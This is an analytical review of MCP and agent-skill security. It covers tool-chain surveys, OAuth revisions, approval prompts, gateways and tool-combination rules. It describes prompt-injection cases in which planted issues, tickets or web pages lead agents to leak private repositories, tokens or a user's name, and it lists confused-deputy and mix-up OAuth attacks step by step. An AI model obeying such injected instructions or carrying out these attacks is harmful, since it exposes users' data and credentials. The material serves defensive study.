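The 4,604 tools that dropped out between the two stages may still be unsafe. Wrong labels cannot explain most of the drop, because the reviewers upheld about 85% of the model's labels in the first stage. About 30% of the servers needed accounts that the team could not easily get, and others needed databases or desktop programs that were hard to set up. The confirmed figure is therefore probably too low for people who have those accounts.

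Only two servers had all three functions. Someone reviewing servers one at a time would therefore almost never find all three together, but a user can combine them by installing three ordinary servers. Different kinds of server tend to supply different functions. Thirty-seven percent of communication and email servers could send data out. Development and testing servers most often reached private data (29%), and social media servers most often read outside content (28%).

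These numbers describe what is available in public directories, and the survey has no data on which servers people install together. If most users have only one or two servers, few may have all three functions, but a single very popular set of servers could expose many people. One rule against data theft relies on the same grouping, since it forbids an agent from holding all three functions at once.

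### From available functions to working chains

Zhao and colleagues built ten chains from popular tools to test whether such tools would work together. Nine chains paired tools from different servers at random, and one used three tools from the same mail server. In each test, a user asked Cursor to do something routine, such as fetch a web page, and the content contained an attacker's instructions. The team ran each chain ten times and checked whether private data reached the attacker.

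The team counted a chain as successful if it worked at least once, and nine of the ten did. By the stricter measure of individual runs, 36 of 100 succeeded. A chain that fetched a web page, read a local file and sent an email worked in eight runs out of ten. One that combined web pages, a work-planning board and a music catalogue never worked. The team thinks the model was less likely to use tools together when their purposes were unrelated. If that is right, counting the available functions overstates the danger, because some possible combinations are too odd for a model to carry out.

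The choice of model made more difference than the choice of application. In a further test of one chain, the team tried seven model settings, five applications and three wordings of the attacker's instructions. GPT-5 and Claude 4.5 Sonnet each resisted the attack in all 75 runs. DeepSeek R1 sent the data in 45 of 60 runs and Gemini 2.5 Flash in 53 of 75. These models all date from 2025. Three fixed wordings are also a weak test of resistance, since a real attacker could keep trying new ones.

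The team had also set the applications to run tools without asking the user, which is fairly realistic. Majeed, Mahmoud and Nadi examined the code of 1,723 applications on GitHub that use MCP servers and found that only 37.2% made the user approve a tool call before it ran (*An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications*, 2026). This figure counts each application once, however many users it has.

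Zhao and colleagues trace the attack to two causes. MCP does not isolate the model's context from its tools, so text from outside can influence which tool the model calls next. MCP also does not enforce least privilege, so once a user has connected a file tool and a mail tool, the agent can use both in a task that only requires reading the news. Removing either cause would stop the theft in this example, because either the attacker's text could not influence later calls or the agent could not use the file and mail tools.

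This explanation comes from analysing how the protocol works, and the survey's counts do not test it. The experiments support it only in part. Both causes were present in every run, yet two of the models never sent any data, so the causes make theft possible but not certain. Still, a user who relies on the model to refuse has no protection when it complies.

### Links that are missing from the code

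Developers often use software to look for security flaws in programs before release. Much of this software starts from a call graph, a map of which functions call which others. If a function that reads a file passes the contents to a function that sends mail, the graph contains a path between them, and the software can follow the data along it.

Two MCP tools usually have no such path between them. Suppose a server has one tool that saves a web page to a folder and another that publishes the files in a folder. Neither tool's code calls the other, and the host's code contains only a general routine that runs whichever tool the model names. The second tool follows the first only if a model or a user chooses that order during a task, so even a perfect call graph of all the source code would leave out this link.

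Zha and colleagues therefore wrote a program, SCAN-MCP, that builds a different graph. Its points are a server's tools, and its arrows are ways in which one tool could affect another. The program works as follows:

1. It finds the code that runs when a model calls each tool.
2. A language model reads this code and notes where untrusted data could enter and where it could do damage, for example by changing a file or leaving over the network.
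3. For every ordered pair of tools on the server, a model judges whether the first could supply data to the second or create a condition that the second needs. If so, the program draws an arrow.
4. Fixed rules keep only paths of two to four tools that start with untrusted input, end in a potentially harmful operation and pass data along at least one arrow.
5. A model drafts a test for each remaining path, with inputs and the effect to expect. The result is a report.

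In the example, an arrow would run from the saving tool to the publishing tool, since the publishing tool can use a file that the saving tool has written. The program also reports flaws within single tools. *ChainFuzzer* (2026), another system for finding such chains, instead starts with tools that can do serious harm and searches backwards for others that could supply their input.

SCAN-MCP's third step relies heavily on a model's judgement, but in a sample of 100 servers, the program rejected 79% of the 9,871 possible links it considered. The team reviewed every remaining link and agreed with about 98% of them.

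The full survey covered 10,121 servers with 90,200 tools, which the team collected between April and July 2025. SCAN-MCP produced 27,123 reports, of which 8,422 (31%) concerned chains. In one chain, a tool for running commands refuses certain dangerous ones, but it checks only the text of the command and not the contents of files the command uses. A second tool on the same server can create files. Either tool could pass a separate review, but an attacker who can use both can get around the restriction.

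In another chain, a browser-control server's tools for opening pages, clicking and uploading files could together send a private file to an attacker's website. The team reported this to the developer of a widely used server, who at first considered it outside the project's security responsibilities. About two weeks later, an update fixed the problem by changing how the server handled uploads. The developer could fix it because all three tools were on one server. When a chain crosses several servers, responsibility for the repair is less clear, since every tool may be working as its author intended.

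### What the manual check confirmed

SCAN-MCP's reports are software predictions that can be wrong, so their number may differ from the number of actual flaws. To measure how often the predictions were right, Zha and colleagues drew a random sample of 100 servers, balanced by source and programming language, for which SCAN-MCP had produced 150 reports. Analysts set up each server on an isolated virtual machine, called the tools and checked whether the predicted effect occurred. They confirmed 105 of the 130 reports about single tools and 19 of the 20 about chains, for a total of 124 (83%). The 26 unconfirmed reports include some that the analysts could not test properly because they lacked an account or a storage service.

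The analysts confirmed 19 of the 20 chain reports they checked, which is a very good result but from a small sample. A standard 95% confidence interval runs from about 76% to 99%, and the true uncertainty is larger because the 19 chains came from only nine servers. The sample also included no reports from servers with at least 50 tools, which accounted for 31% of all chain reports. Multiplying 8,422 by 95% would therefore give a misleadingly exact estimate of the number of real chains.

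Nine of the 100 servers had at least one confirmed chain. This may be the more useful figure because it counts each server once, no matter how many similar reports the server produces. It is probably too low, though. When the team turned off some of SCAN-MCP's filters, the number of chain reports rose from 20 to 96. The analysts confirmed 27 of these, including the original 19 and eight that the filters had removed along with a larger number of false alarms.

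The team tested whether the last tool in a chain could do the damage by itself, in which case the chain report would really be about one bad tool. They reset each server and called only the final tool, with the same attacker's privileges and several kinds of input. This reproduced none of the 19 effects, which is strong evidence that earlier steps were necessary in these cases. It does not show that every step was necessary, because nine of the 20 chain reports involved three or four tools and the team did not test shorter versions of them.

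The team also tested the same 100 servers with three scanners that check each tool separately, and these reported no chains. A language model given the raw code without SCAN-MCP's graph found six of the 19 chains.

The severity of a confirmed chain depends on who can use it. Zha and colleagues assume an attacker who can get the tools called through ordinary prompts or requests. On a shared server, such a chain can give a user access to the host computer. If the server runs on the user's own machine, that user could probably do the same things without any tools, so the chain matters mainly when someone else influences the agent, for instance through prompt injection.

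SCAN-MCP looks for chains only within one server. The results of Zhao and colleagues suggest that the full set of functions needed for data theft is far more common across servers, but they tested only ten chains. Neither survey tests chains across servers on a large scale. Judging every ordered pair among the 90,200 tools would mean about 8.1 billion decisions, nearly all of them about tools that no user has ever installed together. At the rates Zha and colleagues measured for one larger server, this would cost over $3 million and take more than a century on their machine.

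Both samples also omit many MCP servers. *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol Ecosystem* (2025) counted 67,057 servers in public registries in mid-2025, and neither sample includes the internal servers that companies mostly use. An internal server may have better security, or it may have had less outside scrutiny. Neither survey can show which is more common.

### Pairs of agent skills

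In *When Safe Skills Collide*, Wang, Qian and colleagues (2026) also measured combinations of agent skills, using 1,520 skills downloaded from ClawHub, a public registry. They searched each skill's text and code for signs of eight functions and defined ten combinations of these functions as forbidden, such as reading files and sending data over the network.

More than half of the skills (869) matched a forbidden combination by themselves. The other 651 passed, and they form 651 × 650 / 2 = 211,575 pairs. The check flagged a pair if the two skills' combined functions included a forbidden combination, as they would if one skill only read files and the other only used the network. It flagged 47,075 pairs, or 22.25%.

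Most of these turned out to be false alarms. One pair can match several forbidden combinations, so the researchers audited 200 individual matches, 20 for each combination. After weighting for how common each combination was, they estimated that 18.2% of matches were real risks, with a 95% confidence interval from 11% to 27%. Assuming that a pair's matches are either all real or all false, about 4% of the pairs would be risky. One person did the audit after seeing the verdicts of two language models, which may have influenced the result.

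For the most common combination, reading files and sending data out, only two of the 20 audited matches were real. A check at installation that refused all such pairs would take less than a millisecond, but it would block many useful combinations for each dangerous one. Part of the problem is that searching for words is a crude way to detect functions. A skill whose instructions say it needs "no API keys" could be flagged for using them.

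Wang and colleagues also tested whether a risky pair of skills makes a model more likely to agree to a harmful request. They asked six models to download and run a script, changing only the skills in the models' instructions. The models complied in 17 of 18 runs with no skills, 11 of 18 with the risky pair, and 12 of 18 with an unrelated pair. The risky pair evidently did not make the models more likely to agree. But the models could only write replies, not use tools, so the test could not show whether a second skill lets an agent do something it could not do before.

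Xie, Du and colleagues (2026) tested that question in *Benign in Isolation, Harmful in Composition*, using 150 pairs of skills in simulated environments. One skill in each pair finds something, such as a device or an access setting, and the other can act on it. A run counted as harmful only if the agent changed the target that the first skill had found. Averaged over nine models, 1.4% of runs were harmful with only the acting skill, none with only the finding skill, and 33.6% with both, even though the request did not tell the agent to build a harmful chain.

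The scoring requires both a discovery and an action, which a single skill can rarely supply, so the contrast between one skill and two is weaker evidence than the differences between models. With both skills and the same neutral requests, the rate was 0% for Claude Opus 4.5, 48.1% for GPT-5.5 and 91.5% for DeepSeek-V4. A pair of skills that is safe with one model may therefore be dangerous with another, and someone who reviews only the skills will not know which model will use them.

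A second experiment has a fairer comparison, because the harmful action was possible in both conditions. The researchers asked five models to install a harmful skill, either directly or after a review skill had endorsed it. The average installation rate rose from 1.1% to 83.9% with the endorsement. Claude Opus 4.6 was the most cautious of the five, but it went from no installations in 401 trials to 101. The review skill supplied a favourable opinion but no secret data or new access, and the agent treated that opinion as a reason to use access it already had.

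## OAuth tokens, approval prompts and gateways in MCP

In those experiments, whether a combination caused harm depended heavily on the model. Permission rules outside the model avoid this weakness, and MCP has added many since 2024. Most apply to the connection between one client and one server, but many dangerous combinations involve several servers.

### Four revisions of the login rules

MCP launched without an authorization framework, so each server's developer decided whether and how to check who was calling. *MCP has tightened its authentication rules four times* (Dhamsania, 2026) describes the rules that followed.

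The March 2025 version of MCP added a framework based on OAuth 2.1, according to its changelog. OAuth is a standard that lets an application use someone's account without learning the password. The user logs in and approves the request, and the application receives an access token, a string that it attaches to later requests. At first the MCP server logged users in and issued the tokens (Model Context Protocol, 2025). In June 2025 these jobs moved to a separate authorization server. Parecki (2025), who helped with the change, says it made MCP more compatible with existing OAuth systems.

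The June version also dealt with malicious servers that tried to obtain tokens for other services. A client must now use an OAuth resource indicator to name the server it wants a token for, and each server must reject tokens issued for any other. If Alice connects a weather server that turns out to be malicious, her mail server will reject the token that the weather server received from her client. A server also may not forward a client's token to another service. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* explains that forwarding would let callers get around checks such as rate limits and would make the other service's logs misleading about who had called it.

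Another problem was that OAuth's designers had assumed developers would register an application in advance with each service it used. Developers of MCP clients don't know in advance which servers their clients will connect to. The programmer Kenton Varda, quoted by Willison, pointed out in November 2025 that MCP therefore relied on dynamic client registration, in which a client registers itself when it first connects to a server. According to Varda, "practically nobody" had implemented this before MCP.

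Self-registration made one form of the confused deputy attack possible. Suppose an MCP server gives many clients access to an outside calendar service, but identifies itself to the calendar service in the same way for all of them. The attack works like this:

1. Alice approves the MCP server's access to her calendar, and the calendar service stores a cookie in her browser to remember this.
2. An attacker registers a new client with the MCP server, giving the attacker's own website as the return address, and sends Alice a link that starts a login.
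3. Alice clicks. The calendar service finds the cookie and skips the approval screen.
4. The MCP server sends a login code to the attacker, who exchanges it for a token and can use Alice's calendar.

The calendar service had treated approval of the MCP server as approval of everyone using it. A server like this must now ask Alice to approve each client separately, showing her the client's name, the access it requests and the address that will receive the token.

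In November 2025 MCP's maintainers added client metadata documents as the recommended way to identify clients. A client gives a web address as its identity, and the authorization server fetches a description of the client from that address. Only someone who controls the website can publish the description, so the authorization server can decide which domains to trust. This is less secure for clients that run on the user's own computer. A malicious program can give a well-known client's web address and collect the authorization code on the local machine, while the user sees the well-known client's name on the approval screen.

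The July 2026 version deprecated dynamic registration (Model Context Protocol, *Key Changes*, 2026) and added a defence against mix-up attacks. In a mix-up attack, someone who runs one authorization server gets a client to send that server a login code issued by an honest one. The client must now record which authorization server it expects a response from, and compare this with the issuer named in the response before sending the code anywhere. The check does nothing if the honest server leaves out its name, which the rules still permit. Model Context Protocol (2026) notes that these attacks are more common when one client deals with many servers, as in MCP. Like the registration problem, they arise partly because MCP lets any client connect to any server.

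### One token through one call

Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) uses a server at `mcp.example.com` that stores files. If Alice asks her agent to summarise a report on that server, the process is roughly as follows:

1. The client sends a request without a token. The server refuses it and replies that the request needs the scope `files:read`. A scope is a named permission.
2. The client opens Alice's browser at the authorization server and asks for a token for `mcp.example.com` with that scope. Alice logs in and approves.
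3. The browser returns a login code. The client checks the issuer and exchanges the code for a token. It also has to present a secret that it created for this login, so a thief cannot use the code alone.
4. The client repeats its request with the token. The server checks that the token is valid, was issued for this server and covers reading, then returns the report.
5. If the agent later tries to save a file, the server refuses again and names the scope `files:write`. The client asks Alice to approve a new token and retries.

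The token is good evidence that Alice has allowed this client to read files on this server. But suppose the agent reads a salary file and emails it to a supplier. The mail server receives a different token, which is also valid and has a scope such as `mail:send`. Neither token records why the agent made the call, where the text of the message came from or which calls came before it. The mail server can't work this out from the file server's token, which the rules rightly prevent it from receiving.

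Scopes can still prevent this leak if Alice never grants `mail:send`, but then the agent cannot send any email. This protection depends on narrow scopes, and two of MCP's rules tend to widen them. When a server does not specify which scopes a request needs, the client asks for all the scopes the server lists. The official guidance justifies this by the "general-purpose nature of MCP clients", which usually lack the information about a service needed to choose. When a client needs a new scope, it should also request its earlier scopes again to avoid losing them. An agent that needed to delete one file in March may therefore still be able to delete files in June, unless the authorization server or the user reduces the grant.

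The guidance advises servers to list a minimal set of scopes and request more when the agent needs them. It warns that users may abandon an approval screen that lists too many. But each extra request interrupts the user, so server authors, like the authors of browser extensions, have a reason to ask for broad access at the start. The guidance also gives them the option of including scopes they expect the client to need "in the near future".

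All of these rules are optional. A server does not have to require a login, and the OAuth rules do not cover local servers that communicate over standard input and output, which take their credentials from their environment. *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential* (Kale, 2026) cites a scan by the security company Censys that found 12,520 MCP services on the public internet in late April 2026. That count does not show how many of them would give strangers access.

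### Asking a person before each call

A person who approves calls can, in principle, consider the agent's earlier calls, which a token leaves out. If Alice has just watched her agent open the salary file, she may notice the figures in an email to a supplier. But a typical prompt shows only the current call, so she has to remember the earlier one herself, and she may not recognise a total calculated from ten salary files.

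Since March 2025, MCP servers have been able to label a tool as read-only or destructive. This could make approval prompts more useful, because a host could let the agent search freely and ask the user only about deletions. But the host would be relying on the server's author to label the tool correctly. A read-only tool can also contribute to harm when combined with other tools, since reading is the first step in the salary leak.

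The other feature lets a server prompt the user during a call. In an example from the Model Context Protocol release announcement, the server pauses with the prompt "Delete 3 files?" The client collects the answer and sends the original call again with the answer attached. The server can calculate the consequences before it prompts the user, which a host that sees only the request often cannot do. Supabase, a database company, plans to use this to show users the cost of a new project or warn them about a query that would delete data, according to a statement published by Model Context Protocol. Since July 2026, servers may prompt users only while handling a request. However, a malicious server can skip the prompt, and even a trustworthy one has no information about the agent's calls to other servers.

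The more approval prompts users see, the less attention they are likely to give each one. If an agent makes 50 calls in a task and Alice spends ten seconds on each, she will spend more than eight minutes approving work she delegated to save time. An "always allow" button solves this by turning her decision about one call into a standing permission for later calls she has not seen.

TechTarget Japan (2026) reports a conference session in which two specialists warned of this approval fatigue. They noted that a person using an ordinary application clicks a button with a defined effect, while an agent chooses its own tools and their order, so a valid token can lead to operations nobody expected. Asking the user before every important operation would limit this, but they feared people would start approving without checking. The warning is plausible, and Office macro warnings failed for related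 reasons, but the article has no measurements of how often people approve harmful MCP calls or how quickly their attention declines, so it gives no basis for choosing a safe number of prompts.

### Gateways that check the tool's name

A gateway is a program that forwards requests between clients and servers and can refuse some of them. A company can put one gateway in front of 30 servers and write its rules once, without relying on each server's author to apply them.

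The July 2026 version made this easier for remote servers by requiring two labels outside the main body of each request. A call to a search tool carries these:

```
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: search
```

A gateway can let contractors call `search` but not `delete_file` by reading only a request's labels. Servers must reject a request whose labels don't match its body. Without this rule, a client could label a deletion as a search and get it past the gateway.

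Such a rule still applies to one call at a time. An email to a colleague and an email to a supplier both have the name `send_email`. A server can also have clients copy particular arguments into labels, so a gateway could check the recipient's address. But it could not determine whether the message contained salaries without a record of earlier calls.

A gateway is well placed to keep such a memory if all the agent's calls pass through it, but it also needs a way to identify which calls belong to the same task. MCP no longer has sessions, and they were never a reliable way to group calls, since ChatGPT used to start a new one for every tool call. The July version documents a standard way to attach tracing identifiers to requests, which engineers use to follow a call from the host through the servers it reaches. A host could give all the calls in a task the same identifier, but the gateway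 would then depend on the host to do so consistently.

Gateways can also detect some changes that users miss. Dhamsania recommends that gateways store approved tool definitions and raise an alert when one changes. The article says Microsoft and the US National Security Agency independently concluded that identity checks, scopes and logging belong in a layer in front of every server, but this overstates the NSA's confidence. The NSA recommends filtering outgoing traffic through ordinary proxies, but warns that security proxies designed for MCP "remain limited and are still maturing".

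### The NSA on scope and separation

In *Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, its May 2026 guidance on using the protocol safely, the US National Security Agency found that MCP had spread faster than its security model had developed, and that many implementations had no authentication. Those that had it often failed to distinguish between permission to read, create, change and delete. The agency also criticised approval systems that let a server gain new abilities or access to new data after the user has approved it, without asking the user again.

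One of its examples is the server for GitHub, where programmers store code in public or private repositories. Users gave the server blanket access to act for them, so a malicious or compromised tool could read a private repository and publish its contents in a public one. Binding tokens to servers would not have helped, since both operations used the same server. Limiting access to a single repository would have stopped the leak, but a programmer who maintains a public project and a private one may want an agent to work on both.

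Researchers connected an agent to a trusted WhatsApp server and a malicious server. The malicious server displayed a harmless tool description at installation, then replaced it after its second use with one that led the agent to expose the user's messages. The agent already had access to the messages, so the server did not have to steal a WhatsApp token.

The NSA advises organisations to give each server only the access it needs and to explicitly deny it sensitive files and internal networks it does not use. It also advises them to group tools and models by the sensitivity of their data, so that tools for public information, such as weather reports, are separate from tools for health or financial records. Under its guidance, private data should preferably stay with a local server, and a filter should restrict which outside addresses the system can connect to.

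Giving agents separate access to tools and data limits what each agent can combine, unlike issuing access tokens. If no agent has access to both the payroll and the public web, no sequence of calls by one agent can carry salary data from the payroll to the web. The separation also blocks useful tasks. The NSA's guidance introduces MCP with a travel assistant that finds the user's location, looks up visa requirements and recommends flights. If the user's passport details counted as sensitive, the assistant would need a controlled way to use them alongside public websites. The guidance recommends treating data that crosses such boundaries with suspicion, but leaves organisations to decide what may cross.

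The filter on outgoing connections restricts the agent less because it still lets the agent combine tools internally. It would stop the agent from sending the salaries to an unknown website, but not from emailing them through a mail service that the company has approved.

### When a handle is a capability

Since July 2026, MCP has replaced sessions with explicit handles, such as a shopping basket identifier that the model copies from one call to the next. *Sessionless MCP via Explicit State Handles* (Alexander, 2026) explains that sessions had no consistent meaning. Some applications created one per call and others one per launch, so a server's author could not predict how long a basket would last. In a sample of 1,000 open-source servers, 90% did not use the session identifier in their own code, and only 2.5% stored application data under it.

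Handles also let agents share some state and keep the rest separate. Suppose an agent assigns several subagents to shop for one order. They should all add items to the same basket, but each needs its own browser. A shared session would make them share the browser too, while separate sessions would give each its own basket. With handles, the main agent can give them all the same basket identifier and let each create its own browser.

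On a server with no login, anyone who presents the identifier can use the basket, so the identifier is a capability in the security sense as long as nobody can forge it. The specification's example, `bsk_a1b2c3`, would be a poor one, because six lower-case letters and digits allow about 2.2 billion possibilities, which a determined attacker might be able to try. Alexander recommends at least 128 random bits, or about 3.4 × 10³⁸ possibilities.

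If the server requires a login and checks that the basket belongs to the user, the handle is only an identifier, and a stranger who finds it in a chat log cannot use it. Alexander compares it to the address of a Google document, which people can see in their browser history without being able to open the document.

This protection matters because models handle these strings as ordinary text. A model can give away an MCP handle by including it in an email or in its instructions to another agent, unlike a Capsicum capability, which FreeBSD keeps in the operating system and a program cannot give away by printing its number. Kale argues that an attacker can therefore use a planted prompt to steal a working credential. This is true if the server accepts the handle alone, but a server that follows the official rules also checks the user. Sessions could have the same flaw. Alexander notes that MCP's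 Python SDK accepted a session identifier without checking that the caller was the user who created the session. Akamai, a security company, agrees that removing sessions ended one kind of hijacking, but adds that developers now have to protect the state themselves.

Checking the user's permissions leaves the weakness Hardy described at Tymshare. Suppose Alice asks her agent to edit `doc-17`, and a web page it reads contains an instruction to delete `doc-18`, which is also hers. The agent sends `doc-18` with Alice's token. The server confirms that she owns the document and deletes it, so the attacker has used Alice's authority on a document the attacker chose. If each handle were a capability and the agent had received only the one for `doc-17`, it could not have deleted `doc-18`.

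MCP's guidance recommends random handles even for servers with logins, which reduces this risk because an outsider cannot easily guess the handles of Alice's other documents. But Alexander also suggests offering a tool that lists existing objects, in case the model loses a handle. An injected instruction could have the agent call that tool first to get the handles.

Hosts and gateways cannot yet easily limit a task to particular objects, because MCP has no data type for handles. A handle such as a basket identifier looks like any other string in a tool's result. Alexander suggested a label for handles, mainly to help applications keep track of an agent's work, but left it to a future proposal.

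### Whether an agent with a shell needs MCP

In October 2025 the programmer Peter Steinberger, quoted by Willison, argued that having an agent run shell commands was better than MCP for coding. GitHub's MCP server used about 23,000 tokens of the model's context, down from almost 50,000 at launch. GitHub's command-line program, `gh`, did nearly the same work and used no context until the agent ran it. If the agent got a command wrong, the program displayed its help text and the agent tried again. Agents can now load tool descriptions only when they need them, which has weakened the argument about context space. Models' existing knowledge of the commands remains an argument for using the shell.

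Defenders of MCP put more weight on credentials. In June 2026 Sean Lynch wrote, in a comment that Willison republished, that MCP's real advantage over commands and skills was "isolating the auth flow outside of the agent's context window". Lynch thought the ideal MCP might be a gateway that handled authorization for a service and did nothing else. Varda had similarly argued that an agent that wrote its own login code would have access to the token.

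In 2025, the security company Zenity Labs demonstrated an attack that shows why it matters where a credential is stored. The attacker sent a support email that automatically became a ticket in Jira, a system for tracking work. The ticket contained hidden instructions to search the code for a "rotten apple", described as a long string beginning with "eyJ", and send it to the attacker's website. Many access tokens begin with those characters. When a programmer asked the coding agent Cursor to look at the ticket, it sent the string at least some of the time. Cursor had read the ticket through MCP, but MCP could not protect a token left in the code.

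If the host holds the token and the agent never sees it, this theft fails. An attacker can still misuse the agent's access while the agent is running, but cannot copy the token and use it later from another computer. The company can also log each call and disconnect the service. None of this prevents the salary leak, which needs no stolen credential because the agent still has the authority to use the token through its tools.

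The limits on services, which Willison also values, no longer hold if the agent can reach the same service another way. In 2026 Willison tried to change a security rule on his website through the MCP server of Cloudflare, which protects the site. The server could not edit that kind of rule, so he had the agent call Cloudflare's ordinary API instead. He had authorised the change, so no harm was done. But a company that relies on an MCP server to keep an agent from performing certain operations has to make sure that the agent cannot perform them from a shell.

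## Rules that limit which tools an agent may hold together

The simplest way to prevent a dangerous combination of tools is never to give all of them to the same agent. Such a rule applies before the agent makes any calls, so enforcing it requires no record of earlier calls. But it forbids every harmless use of the same combination.

### Three rules for tool sets

The best-known rule dates from June 2025. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, warns against giving one agent all three of these:

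- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content, meaning text or images that an attacker could control
- a way to communicate externally that could carry stolen data out

Zhao and colleagues counted these functions in public MCP servers. Removing any one of them prevents this kind of theft. The third function is easy to overlook, because any tool that makes a web request can put data in the address. Even a link that the user clicks can send data this way.

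Willison would rather remove a function than try to detect attacks, because an attacker can keep trying until something gets past the detector. Willison's *New prompt injection papers* (2025) describes a test of 12 published defences by a team that included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. The attack success rates originally reported for most of the defences were near zero. The team adapted its attacks to each defence and got past most of them over 90% of the time.

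Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turned the warning into a rule for developers. Within one session, an agent may have no more than two of these properties:

- [A] It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- [B] It has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- [C] It can change state or communicate externally.

Changing state includes actions such as deleting a file or making a payment, so the rule covers more than theft. An agent that needs all three properties within one session, without clearing its context, is not allowed to act autonomously. It needs human approval or "another reliable means of validation". Meta intends the rule to apply until research makes it possible to reliably detect and refuse prompt injection.

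*MCP Colors* (Kellogg, 2025) uses only two labels, because the agents Kellogg works on always handle private data. A tool or data source is red if it exposes the agent to untrusted content, and blue if it can take a critical action, such as deleting an email or changing someone's permissions. An agent may have red or blue tools and data sources, but not both colours. Kellogg wrote criteria for the colours and had a language model apply them to about 200 tools. This took about 200 decisions, while reviewing every ordered pair would have taken about 40,000.

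All three rules restrict only tool combinations that involve untrusted content. An agent that misunderstands its task and emails a salary file to a supplier may have read nothing from an outsider, in which case the rules would allow it to hold both the file tool and the mail tool. Meta acknowledges that its rule does not protect against an agent's own mistakes.

### One GitHub server with all three functions

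The NSA's GitHub example involved a malicious or compromised tool, but the same leak can happen when every tool is trustworthy. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes a May 2025 demonstration in which the security company connected Claude Desktop to GitHub's official MCP server, using a test account with a public repository and several private ones.

Anyone can file an issue, such as a bug report, in a public repository. The researchers filed one that contained instructions for an agent, then asked the agent to look at the open issues. The agent read the instructions and collected information from the private repositories. It put this information in a pull request (a proposed change to the code) in the public repository, where anyone could see it. The leak included the fictional user's salary and plans to relocate.

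The server had no bug. Heise's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains that it worked through the user's account, so the agent could also access the private repositories. By default, Claude Desktop asked the user to confirm each call, but Invariant Labs notes that many people choose "Always Allow". The model was Claude 4 Opus, which Anthropic has since replaced with more resistant models.

A rule that counted servers would have missed this combination, because there was only one server. Someone has to label each tool, and even those labels may not be precise enough, because a tool for reading files can return private data from one repository and an attacker's text from another, depending on the call's arguments. With accurate labels, Willison's and Kellogg's rules would both forbid this agent, and Meta's would require supervision.

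The rules diverge if the user limits the agent to the public repository. The agent then has no private data to steal, so it no longer meets Willison's three conditions. If changing code counts as a critical action, Kellogg's rule still forbids the agent to both read strangers' issues and change the code, though it must do both to fix a reported bug.

Invariant Labs proposed a narrower rule that limits an agent to one repository per session. A checker compares the repository in each call with the one in earlier calls and blocks the call if they differ. The agent can still read a bug report and propose a fix, but it cannot copy private code into a public repository. It also cannot do tasks that span repositories, such as updating a program together with a library it depends on. The rule covers only GitHub calls, so an agent with a mail tool could still email the code out.

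GitHub (2025) later announced a lockdown mode that removes the untrusted content instead. In this mode, an agent working on a public repository receives content only from people with push access, the right to change the repository's code. This blocks an attacker's issue, but also genuine bug reports from strangers. DevClass's *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* had called an earlier proposal for such a filter "interesting but crude" for this reason.

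### Answering customers' email

Suppose an online shop wants an agent to answer email. A customer asks where an order is, and the agent looks it up in the shop's internal database and replies. This ordinary task requires the agent to read strangers' messages, access private data and send messages. Bowley, in *Does the “lethal trifecta” kill the idea of fully autonomous AI Agents*, uses customer records and customers' emails as examples of things that make an agent very risky when combined.

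Willison's rule forbids this agent. Kellogg's does too if a reply is a critical action, as it should be when it could contain other customers' records. Meta's rule leaves the shop some choices, which Meta worked out for an email assistant:

| Restriction | Effect on the shop |
|---|---|
| The agent reads mail only from trusted senders | It cannot help most customers |
| The agent has no access to private data | It can give the opening hours but cannot find an order |
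| A person approves each reply | It can do the whole task, but staff have to check its work |

Approval preserves the most usefulness, but the employee who checks a reply may miss an attack. In a study that Anthropic published in August 2026, 1,053 paid developers worked with a coding agent that asked them to approve its actions. Partway through each session, the agent asked to run a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% of the developers refused, according to Willison in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*. The shop's employees might do better, since checking an email differs from checking a command. Still, the result shows how little protection an approval step can give, and Meta itself mentions users who blindly confirm a warning.

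The shop could also limit what the tools can do. Software outside the model could restrict each lookup to the orders of the customer who wrote, and allow a reply only to that customer's address. An attacker who wrote to the shop could then get only their own records. The agent would still have all three functions according to its labels, however.

### What labels miss

Kellogg offers two ways to make labels less coarse. Developers could remove a tool's red label if something validates its output, much as a website checks what people enter in a form. Kellogg thinks most people would trust a text that ten humans had reviewed, but leaves open whether one person or a language model would be enough. A colleague suggested grading each colour from 1 to 5 and letting users set their own limits. This would permit more combinations of tools, but someone would have to define each grade.

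Hosts could apply such rules automatically if tools came with reliable labels. Model Context Protocol (2026) lists proposals from GitHub and OpenAI for labels covering trust and secrecy. The two companies developed these proposals after finding gaps in MCP while using it in their products. The maintainers argue that a tool's risk depends on how its labels interact with those of other tools in the session. A host would have to trust whoever supplied the labels, as with MCP's existing read-only label.

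One tool can also have several functions. An email tool gives an agent access to private messages, exposes it to text from strangers and lets it send data out, so it can violate Willison's rule by itself. A tool that fetches web pages can also send data out, in the addresses it requests. Anthropic had limited Claude's web-fetching tool to certain addresses to prevent this, but it also let the tool follow links on pages it had already fetched. In July 2026 Willison reported on an attack that used this exception. A malicious website offered a link for each letter of the alphabet, and Claude revealed the user's name by following the links that spelled it. Anthropic has since removed the exception.

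Data theft is also only one kind of harm, as Willison acknowledges. An attacker who gets an agent to delete a database does harm without receiving any data. Willison therefore welcomed Meta's addition of state changes, but objected that Meta's diagram labelled the combination of untrusted input and state changes "safe". Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that property B covers any sensitive system, so an agent without B could change things only where the changes did not matter, such as in a sandbox. Meta also replaced "safe" with "lower risk".

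This reply makes the Rule of Two stricter than it first appears, and close to Kellogg's rule. If B covers every system worth protecting, an agent that can change one of them already has B and C, so it may not read untrusted content without supervision.

### A policy for the whole chain

More detailed labels let a system calculate which tools are compatible. *Securing Multi-Tool AI Agent Chains With Dynamic, Real-Time Compositional Policies* (Schneider, Faujdar and colleagues, 2026) describes such a system from Microsoft, the Dynamic Security Control Compositor (DSCC). Each tool has a policy that rates the sensitivity of its data on a scale from Public through Internal and Confidential to Restricted. The policy also states whether the data must stay inside the organisation, whether the tool sends data out, which network zones the tool may run in and how long a session may last. It sets security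 controls from a US government catalogue to allow, restrict or deny.

Before a session starts, DSCC combines the policies of all the tools the agent will use and takes the strictest value of each part. If tool *i* has sensitivity Cᵢ, permitted zones Zᵢ and maximum session length Tᵢ, the policy for *n* tools is:

- C = max(C₁, …, Cₙ)
- Z = Z₁ ∩ … ∩ Zₙ, the zones that every tool permits
- T = min(T₁, …, Tₙ)

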